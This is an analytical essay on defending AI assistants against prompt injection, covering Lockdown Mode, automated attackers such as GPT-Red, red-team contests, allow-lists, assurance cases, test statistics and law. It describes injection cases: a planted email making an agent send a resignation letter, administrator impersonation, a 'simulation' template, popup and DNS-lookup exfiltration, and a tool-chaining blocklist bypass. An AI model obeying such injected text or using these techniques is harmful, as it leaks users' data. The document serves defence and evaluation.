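Scanners find paths that an injection could use, but they don't show whether a model would follow one. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an LLM attacker trained to find injections that work on the Atlas browser's agent. OpenAI trained it with reinforcement learning, rewarding it for successful attempts. The attacker proposes an injection, and a simulator runs the agent as if it had encountered that text. The attacker then receives a record of the agent's reasoning and actions, revises the injection and tries again.

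In OpenAI's demonstration, the automated attacker planted an email telling the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and sent the letter. OpenAI says the attacker could lead the agent through tens or hundreds of steps and found strategies that had not appeared in OpenAI's human testing or in outside reports. OpenAI responded with a newly trained model and stronger safeguards. It did not say how many attacks the system had found or how often they worked.

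*GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) describes a later OpenAI attacker trained against several defending models at once, as those models learned to resist it. On scenarios from a public hacking contest, GPT-Red found more working attacks on GPT-5.1 than the human contestants had. It also attacked a vending machine business run by an AI agent in OpenAI's office. After practising in a simulation, it posed as an administrator and got the live agent to cut a product's price to $0.50.

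OpenAI then trained GPT-5.6 on GPT-Red's attacks. GPT-Red's success rate on the contest scenarios fell below 4%, even without the protections a product would add around the model. This result does not show how GPT-5.6 would handle attacks unlike the ones it trained on. Attacks in PromptArmor's benchmark still sometimes succeeded against GPT-6 Astra, a newer OpenAI model.

GPT-Red usually receives a goal and a fixed place to put its text, such as one search result, and mainly looks for wording that the model will obey. This can show whether Alice's assistant would follow Victor's email, but it is unlikely to reveal an unknown outbound channel such as the preview's popups. Wallace and colleagues acknowledge that people may find scenarios or types of attack that GPT-Red does not cover.

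Trained attackers also tend to repeat attacks that work. *PIPETTE* (2026) describes this problem and rewards its attacker for variety to counter it. Wallace and colleagues saw the same repetition when they trained an attacker against a single defender, and found that using defenders with different weaknesses led to more varied attacks. *AutoPI* (2026) distinguishes an attacker's success rate from its coverage, the number of distinct ways it can make an injection work. Neither is a measure of how many outbound channels the attacks use.

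### Contests and bug bounties

A red team attacks a system with its owner's permission. In *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) describe the red-team contest they ran, which later supplied GPT-Red's scenarios. In the contest, 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times, or 3.2%. The prize fund was $40,000, less than $5 for each successful attack. To succeed, most attacks had to make the agent do something harmful and hide it from the user.

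Success rates ranged from 0.5% against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Gemini 2.5 Pro. Successes rose roughly in proportion to attempts throughout the contest, so the contestants showed no sign of running out of working attacks. Many of those attacks were variations on the same idea, though. In 21 of the 41 scenarios, contestants succeeded with near-identical versions of one template, in which they told the model that it was in a simulation.

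The organisers chose the harmful action and where the injection went in every scenario, so the contestants found many ways to persuade a model but had little opportunity to discover a new channel. Check Point's researchers had that opportunity because they could investigate any part of ChatGPT, including its browser frames and package service. A vendor that wants to find unknown channels should give its red team the same freedom and access to the source code.

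Bug bounties pay outsiders who report flaws. On 25 March, OpenAI (2026) launched a Safety Bug Bounty that covers data theft through prompt injection. To qualify, an attack must work at least 50% of the time. This rule spares OpenAI from investigating flukes, but it excludes less reliable attacks that could still do a lot of damage if sent to many people.

OpenAI also runs a separate bounty for conventional security flaws and may move reports between the two, so a report sent to the wrong program can still be considered. Scope can still be a problem when a flaw depends on several components. The browser-control developers initially rejected a real attack path as out of scope. Bounties also mostly find flaws after release, when attackers can be looking for them too.

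### The day a preview is added

A forbid-list blocks listed actions and permits all others, while an allow-list permits only listed actions. OpenAI describes Lockdown Mode as a setting that "limits or turns off certain features", which makes it a forbid-list.

Zha and colleagues found a server whose blocklist could be bypassed by combining two tools. One tool ran commands but refused any that contained dangerous words such as `rm`, which deletes files. The other could write files. An attacker could write a script containing `rm` and then use the first tool to run it, because the command contained only the script's harmless-looking name. An allowlist of a few safe commands would have blocked the script, provided none of those commands could run scripts.

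Suppose a vendor adds a web page preview with the popup flaw to a chat product that has a protected mode:

| Event | Forbid-list | Allow-list |
|---|---|---|
| The vendor releases the preview | It works in protected chats because the list does not mention it | It stays off, and users in protected chats see the page's code as text |
| A hostile page tries to open a popup that day | The popup opens and can send out the chat | The page does not run |
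| Nobody reviews the preview | It stays on | It stays off |
| A reviewer finds the flaw | The vendor blocks or repairs the preview, but users have already been exposed | The vendor repairs the preview before turning it on |
| A reviewer misses the flaw | Users remain exposed | Exposure begins when the reviewer approves the preview |

A delay in reviewing the preview leaves private data at risk under a forbid-list, but under an allow-list it only leaves users without a convenience. People who turn on a protected mode have already accepted some loss of convenience, so an allow-list suits them better.

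An allow-list still depends on competent review, and its entries have to be specific. OpenAI put its preview inside code blocks, so an allow-list that already included "code blocks" might have permitted it. A safer entry would let code blocks display text but not run scripts, make network requests or open new windows.

### When to repeat the analysis

A new feature can complete an attack path whose other steps reviewers have already approved. Each release therefore needs a fresh analysis of the whole set of capabilities. Some changes that users never notice also need one:

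| Change | What reviewers should check | Earlier example |
|---|---|---|
| A new renderer, which displays or runs content | What the content can load, run or open in each browser and app | ChatGPT's web page preview |
| A new app action | Who can see the result, and what the assistant can choose | The comment that Victor read |
| A new shared internal service | Whether one customer's session can affect what another's reads | The package service in ChatGPT's sandbox |
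| A new permitted destination | Who else can receive data there | Uploads to Anthropic's own domain |
| A wider audience for an existing location | Whether outsiders can now see what the assistant writes | Victor's invitation to the ticket tracker |

Engineers need to trigger a review when they connect a new service to the sandbox, because reviewers who wait for product announcements would miss a shared service like the one Check Point Research exploited. Reviewers also need to check each app's renderer separately, because a popup that required a click in a web browser could open without one in ChatGPT's desktop app.

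Automatic analysis is cheap enough to repeat whenever a server changes. On a server with 22 tools, SCAN-MCP had 462 ordered pairs to compare, at about $0.0004 each, or 19 cents in total. A new tool would add 44 pairs and about two cents, plus the cost of examining any new chains. Confirming the reports by hand accounts for most of the expense. Zha and colleagues suggest that marketplaces scan servers when they first list them and again after updates, and that developers add the scan to their routine automated tests.

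### Does automated search favour defenders?

AI systems can now find some multi-step attacks. SCAN-MCP's LLM proposed attack chains within a single server, which people then had to test and confirm. OpenAI's AI attackers led agents through long sequences of harmful actions, but they worked towards set goals. Neither system has been shown to discover by itself an unknown way to get data out of a finished product such as ChatGPT.

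A vendor can search before release, with access to source code and to reasoning records that outsiders cannot see. It can also close a path for all its customers at once. An attacker needs only one path that the vendor missed. Suppose a release has *k* paths. The vendor closes each with probability *d*, and attackers find each remaining one with probability *a*. If all these events are independent, the chance that attackers find at least one path is

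1 − (1 − *a*(1 − *d*))ᵏ.

With five paths and *a* = 30%, that chance is 83% if the vendor does not search and 27% if it closes each path with probability *d* = 80%. If AI doubles *a* to 60%, the chance rises to 47%, but it falls to 14% if the vendor also raises *d* to 95%. These numbers are illustrative, but they show that better tools for both sides can leave users safer if the vendor uses them before release.

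The vendor's and the attacker's searches would not be fully independent. An attacker who runs the vendor's own scanner will mostly find paths the vendor has already closed, but one who runs a different scanner may find paths that are still open. In Zha and colleagues' comparison, AI-Infra-Guard found 43 confirmed single-tool flaws that SCAN-MCP missed, even though SCAN-MCP found more overall. A vendor should therefore use several methods and accept the extra false alarms.

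Automated search probably helps defenders more in a product like ChatGPT, where one company controls the code and can fix it centrally. Public tool servers are more exposed because attackers can read their code, and thousands of separate developers would each have to run a scanner and fix what it found. Zha and colleagues estimate that the first stage of their analysis, which locates the code behind each tool, would cost $631 for all 90,200 tools in their collection, an amount an attacker could afford as easily as a marketplace could.

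## What can a vendor truthfully claim about such a control?

A vendor that has searched its product for attack paths knows which ones it closed, but not how many it missed. It can still make true and useful claims about a lockdown setting if the evidence supports them. The table lists four possible claims, from weakest to strongest, and compares them with what OpenAI has published about Lockdown Mode.

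| Claim | Evidence it needs | What the published evidence supports |
|---|---|---|
| Feature claim: the setting blocks the listed features | A check that ordinary software turns each feature off and the model cannot turn it back on | Good support, since users can see for themselves that agent mode and deep research are gone |
| Channel claim: no request leaves through the listed channels | Network rules, and tests that look for traffic at the receiving end | Plausible for browsing, though OpenAI describes the design without reporting tests |
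| Conditional claim: no data leaves if stated assumptions hold | A complete list of channels, a list of assumptions, and an argument from these to the conclusion | No support, since OpenAI's announcement and help page contain neither list |
| Absolute claim: no data leaves | No evidence could be enough | None, and OpenAI disclaims it |

Outsiders can test a channel claim. They set up a web server, invent an address on it that nobody has used, and try to get ChatGPT to open that address in Lockdown Mode. They watch the server's log for several weeks, in case a crawler fetches the address later. A single request for the address disproves the claim, but if none appears, the test supports the claim only for the methods they tried.

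Customers can lose data even when a channel claim is true. ChatGPT's code container blocked direct web requests, but Check Point Research still sent data out of it through domain name lookups. To make a conditional claim, the vendor would have had to block those lookups or state the assumption that nobody could misuse them.

Until OpenAI fixed the web page preview on 18 September 2026, a conditional claim about Lockdown Mode would also have been false unless it excluded previews. Eli Smadja of Check Point told The Hacker News that the preview had provided "an alternative path around that security boundary".

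The absolute claim covers channels nobody has thought of, so no test or proof can establish it. It is also false in any workspace where an administrator has let the assistant write to an app that outsiders can read.

### A precedent for publishing assumptions

Developers of other software have publicly made conditional claims. seL4 is a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that controls which programs may use which memory and devices. Its developers have a machine-checked proof about its code. *What the Proofs Assume*, which they also publish, lists the possible sources of failure that remain, including about 340 lines of low-level code for ARM processors, about 1,200 lines of start-up code, and hardware that might not work as documented.

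In the entry on secrecy, the developers write that their proof that secrets do not leak assumes their hardware model includes every relevant information channel, and that they know this to be untrue. They add that proofs of this kind "can never be absolute". The proof is still valid, but its conclusion holds only for channels in the model, which in practice include storage inside the kernel but not timing.

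This candour is useful because a customer can examine a short list of assumptions instead of thousands of lines of code. OpenAI's warning about "unforeseen combinations of capabilities" gives a customer nothing to examine. An entry in the style of seL4's might read, "We assume that nothing ChatGPT displays can open a connection from the user's computer." A tester could have checked that assumption and found the popup.

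seL4 also warns that its proved properties differ between platforms and configurations. Andronick, in *What's verified, what's not, and what does it mean?*, cautions against two easy inferences. Someone who has downloaded seL4 may not have a verified configuration, and someone with a verified kernel may have built an insecure system on top of it. A company that has turned on Lockdown Mode can make a similar mistake if nobody asks which apps the administrator left on.

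### An assurance case for a lockdown setting

An assurance case is a structured argument that a system has a certain property. It states the claim, the reasoning and evidence for it, and any known reasons for doubt. Engineers write assurance cases for nuclear plants, railways and aircraft. The example below is for an imaginary AI assistant, and its evidence is invented.

| Part | Content |
|---|---|
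| Version and date | Web version 8.3, assessed on 1 December 2026. The case lapses on 1 March 2027, or earlier if the vendor releases a new version. |
| Configuration | Lockdown is on for all staff, who cannot turn it off for single chats. The mail and wiki apps are read-only. Other apps, memory and page previews are off. |
| Threat model | The attacker can write emails, files and web pages that the assistant reads, can open an account with the vendor, and knows these rules. The attacker cannot log in as a member of staff or change the vendor's software. |
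| Claim | An injection cannot make the assistant send company data to anyone except the mail and wiki providers, which receive search terms. |
| Argument | Data could leave through browsing, code, displayed answers or apps. Browsing uses stored copies, and the crawler ignores addresses from chats. Code has no network access, cannot look up domain names and shares no services with other customers. Answers appear as plain text without links. Neither app accepts write actions. |
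| Evidence | A review of the network rules and display code; 5,000 invented web addresses in 40 formats, none of which received a request within 30 days; a six-week attack by an outside team with the source code |
| Exclusions | Desktop and phone apps, the vendor's coding assistant, leaks through timing, wrong answers, and staff who copy data out themselves |
| Reasons for doubt | The outside team tested domain name lookups in only one of three data centres. Nobody has checked whether crash reports, which go to another company, contain text from chats. |

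The vendor has to resolve each doubt or narrow the claim. It could test the other two data centres, for example, or limit the claim to customers served from the first. If crash reports contain text from chats, the claim is false, and the vendor must change the reports or the claim.

The format also shows which later changes would matter. If an administrator lets the assistant comment on tickets, the last sentence of the argument is no longer true, and someone like Victor may be able to read the result. If the vendor turns on page previews, the review of its network rules no longer covers every channel, because a popup connects to the internet from the user's own computer.

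An assurance case can become paperwork that defends a predetermined conclusion. Haddon-Cave's *The Nimrod Review* (2009) examined the safety case for a British military aircraft that caught fire in 2006, killing 14 people. It found that many people believed the aircraft was safe anyway, which had undermined the work. A vendor can guard against this by paying someone to look for reasons for doubt and publishing any it can't resolve.

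### What a clean test can show

Suppose a vendor runs *n* independent random trials and none of them leaks data. If the true failure rate is *p*, the chance of such a clean run is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of *p* at which this chance falls to 5%:

(1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05, so *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*

The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3. With 300 clean trials, the bound is 1%. A bound of one in a million would take three million clean trials.

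The trials also have to be independent. Anthropic hired Trajectory Labs to test auto mode, the automated reviewer in its coding assistant Claude Code. The testers ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 5 or either of two other Claude models. If all 720 attempts were independent, the bound would be about 0.4%. If the ten attempts at each scenario always had the same outcome, there would effectively be only 72 trials, and the bound would be about 4%.

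Auto mode relies on classifiers, so repeating a scenario can produce a different result. Repeating a test reveals much less about a deterministic control, because a fixed rule handles the same request the same way every time. Trying one forbidden address 300 times is close to running a single test, and a vendor would learn more from 300 different kinds of request, spread across file types, apps and devices.

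### Why the bound does not cover an attacker

The 3/*n* bound applies to inputs drawn at random from the same population as the tests, but an attacker chooses the input. Suppose one input in a million gets past a fixed rule. A test with 300 random inputs will miss all such inputs 99.97% of the time, so the vendor can correctly report that the failure rate is probably below 1%. Because the rule is fixed, an attacker who finds one of these inputs can use it successfully every time.

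Check Point's researchers bypassed Lockdown Mode with an input of this sort. They studied how the preview worked and wrote a web page that got around its approval step, which a random page would almost never do.

On 7 August 2026, Anthropic published its result of zero successes in 720 attempts. Nineteen days later, Rehberger published an attack on Opus 5 in auto mode. Willison (2026), in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, described Rehberger as one of the most credible researchers in the field. Crosley, in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, reports that the main version of the attack worked in three of five runs, and that two configurations of another version worked in three of five and four of five.

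Rehberger cautioned that these are small samples. But even three successes in five runs give a 95% confidence interval of about 15% to 95%, far above the 0.4% bound. The two results are compatible because they are for different attacks. The 720 attempts used attacks optimised against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, while Rehberger designed his for the system he was attacking.

### What "substantially reduces" leaves out

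To interpret a claimed reduction, a reader needs to know the failure rate without the control and which attacks produced it. Anthropic's published figures show how much this matters. The safeguards in the table are probabilistic defences, mainly probes that scan incoming text for injections, and the last column gives the percentage by which they cut the attack success rate.

| Model and test | Success without safeguards | Success with safeguards | Reduction |
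|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, browser attacks used in November 2025 | 8.0% | 1.4% | 83% |
| Opus 4.5, later browser attacks by professionals | 17.6% | 16.7% | 5% |
| Opus 5, coding, earlier automated attacker | 2.68% | 0.39% | 85% |
| Opus 5, coding, stronger automated attacker | 90.93% | 18.21% | 80% |
| Sonnet 5, coding, stronger automated attacker | 19.47% | 15.76% | 19% |

The November 2025 figures come from Anthropic's account of its browser defences. The later browser figures, in Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*, are for the strongest safeguards it had that November. Anthropic could fairly have said that its safeguards substantially reduced the risk from the original attacks, but they made almost no difference against the later, harder ones. The tests differed in other ways, including how they measured success, so the harder attacks may not explain the whole change.

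Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports the coding results. Both automated attackers made 200 attempts at each of the same 40 scenarios, but the stronger one had trained for longer and on more varied attacks. Its success rate against Opus 5 was 34 times higher than the weaker one's. The probes' measured benefit also depends on the metric. They stopped 80% of the stronger attacker's successful attempts on Opus 5, but the attacker still succeeded at least once in all 40 scenarios, so the number of vulnerable scenarios did not fall.

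Anthropic considers this attacker unrealistically strong because the attacker trained on the test scenarios and could try many times. Anthropic also warns that fixed sets of known attacks can give "a false sense of security". It had already retired one browser test after attacks on its newest models succeeded 0% of the time without extra safeguards. On the harder test that replaced it, attacks succeeded 3.8% of the time against Opus 5 before Anthropic added safeguards.

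OpenAI gives neither a baseline nor an attack set for Lockdown Mode. It could provide both by saying, for example: "In version 8.3, testers who knew Lockdown Mode's rules found 200 attacks that stole data with the mode off. With it on, 12 of those attacks succeeded after the testers had a week to adapt each one." Readers could then calculate a 94% reduction for those attacks and judge whether the testers resembled the attackers that worry them.

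### How vendors word their promises

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode shares its name with an older Apple setting for phones and computers. According to Apple's *Lockdown Mode support*, Apple's version strictly limits certain apps, websites and features to give spyware fewer ways in. Apple also says the mode sacrifices functionality, performance or both. *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes Microsoft's approach, which combines probabilistic defences with deterministic blocking of known exfiltration methods.

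| Vendor and product | Promise | Stated limit |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, Lockdown Mode | Designed to "substantially reduce the risk" of data theft through injection | No guarantee, and three ways in which risk may remain |
| Anthropic, auto mode in Claude Code | Reduces risk for most users | "does not eliminate risk" |
| Anthropic, Claude in Chrome | Defends against current attacks | Prompt injection "remains a moving target" |
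| Google, AI agent in Chrome | Makes it "difficult and costly for attackers to cause harm" | Injection is an "open challenge" |
| Microsoft, AI products | Blocks known methods of exfiltration by fixed rule | Covers methods that are already known |
| Apple, Lockdown Mode | "helps protect devices" against rare and sophisticated attacks | Complete protection requires the latest software |

None of these vendors makes the absolute claim. OpenAI is the most specific about where risk remains, and Anthropic gives the most figures. Google's promise concerns the attacker's effort, so testing it would require estimating how much time or money an attack takes. Microsoft's promise is close to a channel claim, but the word "known" limits it significantly.

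Vendors' published measurements of prompt injection are hard to compare. In June 2026, VentureBeat's *Anthropic browser agent hijacked 31 percent before safeguards engaged* described the vendors' safety documents. Anthropic reported injection tests for four kinds of task and showed how attackers' success rate rose with repeated attempts. OpenAI's document for GPT-5.5 reported a single score from one test, which used known attacks on connectors. Google published no injection results for Gemini 3. OpenAI has separately published results from its automated attacker GPT-Red, but these measure the model's resistance, not Lockdown Mode.

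Attack success rates are a suitable measure for Anthropic's classifiers, which sometimes fail on attacks they usually stop. For a deterministic control, a customer would learn more from a list of the channels through which data could leave and the rule that closes each one. OpenAI has published part of such a list.

Careful wording often gets lost when others repeat it. An Apple spokesperson said in March 2026 that the company was "not aware of any successful mercenary spyware attacks" on devices in Lockdown Mode. MacTech reported this under the headline *Apple no one using Lockdown Mode has ever been hacked with spyware* (2026), which is a claim about every user, although Apple can know only about detected attacks.

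The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* bases its headline on a test in which no attack succeeded in 129 scenarios. If those scenarios were a random sample, the 95% upper bound on the attack success rate would be 2.3%. The article explains that the result depended on auto mode. Willison quotes an Anthropic employee who wrote that the company should have called its auto mode announcement "defeating the lethal trifecta", but the announcement itself claimed much less.

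### What the law adds

In the United States, section 5 of the Federal Trade Commission Act bans deceptive commercial practices. Under a 1983 policy statement from the Federal Trade Commission (FTC), a claim is deceptive if it is likely to mislead customers who act reasonably and could affect their decisions. The FTC also expects a company to have a reasonable basis for an objective claim before making it.

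The FTC has applied these rules to security and AI products. In 2020 it accused the video service Zoom of promising end-to-end encryption while keeping keys that could have let it access customers' meetings. In 2025 it accused Workado of advertising its AI-text detector as 98% accurate, when independent testing had found 53% accuracy on general-purpose text. According to the FTC, the detector worked properly only on academic writing. A vendor that presented a success rate from one set of injections as a general measure of security could face a similar complaint.

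OpenAI's wording is much safer than Zoom's, because OpenAI promises only a reduction and says it does not guarantee more. OpenAI still needs a reasonable basis for the word "substantially". The law does not generally require it to publish that basis, so a customer who wants to see it has to ask.

Article 15 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to have an appropriate level of accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity. They must resist outsiders who try to alter their use or outputs, including through inputs designed to make a model err. Article 13 requires the instructions for use to state what level of cybersecurity the provider has tested and which foreseeable circumstances could affect it. These instructions would contain much of the same information as an assurance case.

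High-risk systems include those for recruitment, credit scoring and law enforcement. A general assistant does not become high-risk just because it can read private mail, so many uses of Lockdown Mode fall outside Article 15. An amendment that came into force on 27 July 2026 postponed these duties until 2 December 2027 for systems that are high-risk because of their use, and until 2 August 2028 for AI in certain products, such as lifts, that other EU safety laws already regulate.

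The EU's Cyber Resilience Act covers hardware and software that connect to a device or network. Manufacturers must assess cybersecurity risks, limit the ways an attacker could get in, and tell users about foreseeable circumstances that could create significant risks. Most of these duties begin on 11 December 2027. The act also covers remote services that a product needs in order to work, but generally not standalone online services. ChatGPT's desktop and phone apps are therefore more likely to be covered than ChatGPT in a browser.

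Since 11 September 2026, manufacturers have had to report any vulnerability in a covered product that attackers are actively exploiting. They must send a first warning within 24 hours of learning of the exploitation. OpenAI repaired the preview a week after this duty began. The duty probably did not apply, because there was no evidence that anyone had used the flaw outside Check Point's research. Customers therefore can't assume that this law will reveal every serious bypass.

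### Do caveats shift risk to customers?

A critic could say that OpenAI benefits from a reassuring name while its disclaimer leaves customers to bear the loss. The name "Lockdown" suggests that nothing gets out, but OpenAI says in the frequently asked questions near the end of its help page that the mode does not guarantee this. The FTC warned in its 1983 policy that fine print may not correct a misleading impression. OpenAI has also written that users should be able to decide whether to accept the risks of network features, but nobody has measured those risks, so users can't judge them.

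False confidence could leave some people worse off. If the mode cuts the chance of theft by 80%, but a lawyer who trusts it uploads files ten times as valuable as before, the expected loss doubles (0.2 × 10 = 2).

Without a partial claim, a vendor could often make no claim at all, which would be worse. If OpenAI offered the mode without a disclaimer, customers would have less reason to examine their apps. Waiting until it could guarantee that no data leaves would deprive them of a control that closes several known channels. Anthropic took a similar view when it published its browser results in November 2025, writing that a 1% attack success rate was still "meaningful risk" and that no browser agent was immune to injection.

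How fair a caveat is depends on who can act on it. An administrator can act on the warning about enabled apps. Customers can do little about newly discovered techniques, so a caveat about those mostly protects the vendor unless the vendor takes on more of the work. It should review each new feature before allowing it in the mode, publish the date of its last full review, and tell customers when someone finds a bypass.

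The name is harder to defend, though Apple had made it familiar before OpenAI used it. A line beside the switch, such as "Limits web access. Enabled apps can still send data out", would correct the most likely misunderstanding when it matters.

### Questions for a buyer

A company considering a lockdown setting should put these questions to the vendor in writing:

- Which products, apps and devices does the setting cover? Lockdown Mode does not affect network access in Codex, for example.
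- Who can turn it off, and can an administrator prevent that for single chats?
- Which outbound channels has the vendor identified, and what closes each one? The answer should include domain name lookups, displayed content, crash reports and services shared with other customers.
- What does the vendor assume, and which of those assumptions does it know to be false or untested?
- Is a new feature on or off in the protected mode before anyone has reviewed it?
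- When did someone last review the whole set of features together, and in which version?
- If the vendor says that the setting reduces risk, what was the success rate without it, and which attacks did the testers use?
- Did the testers know the rules, have the source code and get time to adapt? How many different attacks did they try, leaving out repetitions?
- Which bypasses have people reported, how long was each one open, and how did customers find out?
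- If data leaks through the vendor's own servers, what records will exist, how long will the vendor keep them, and will it search them for a customer?
- What will the vendor pay if the setting fails while the customer is using it as instructed?
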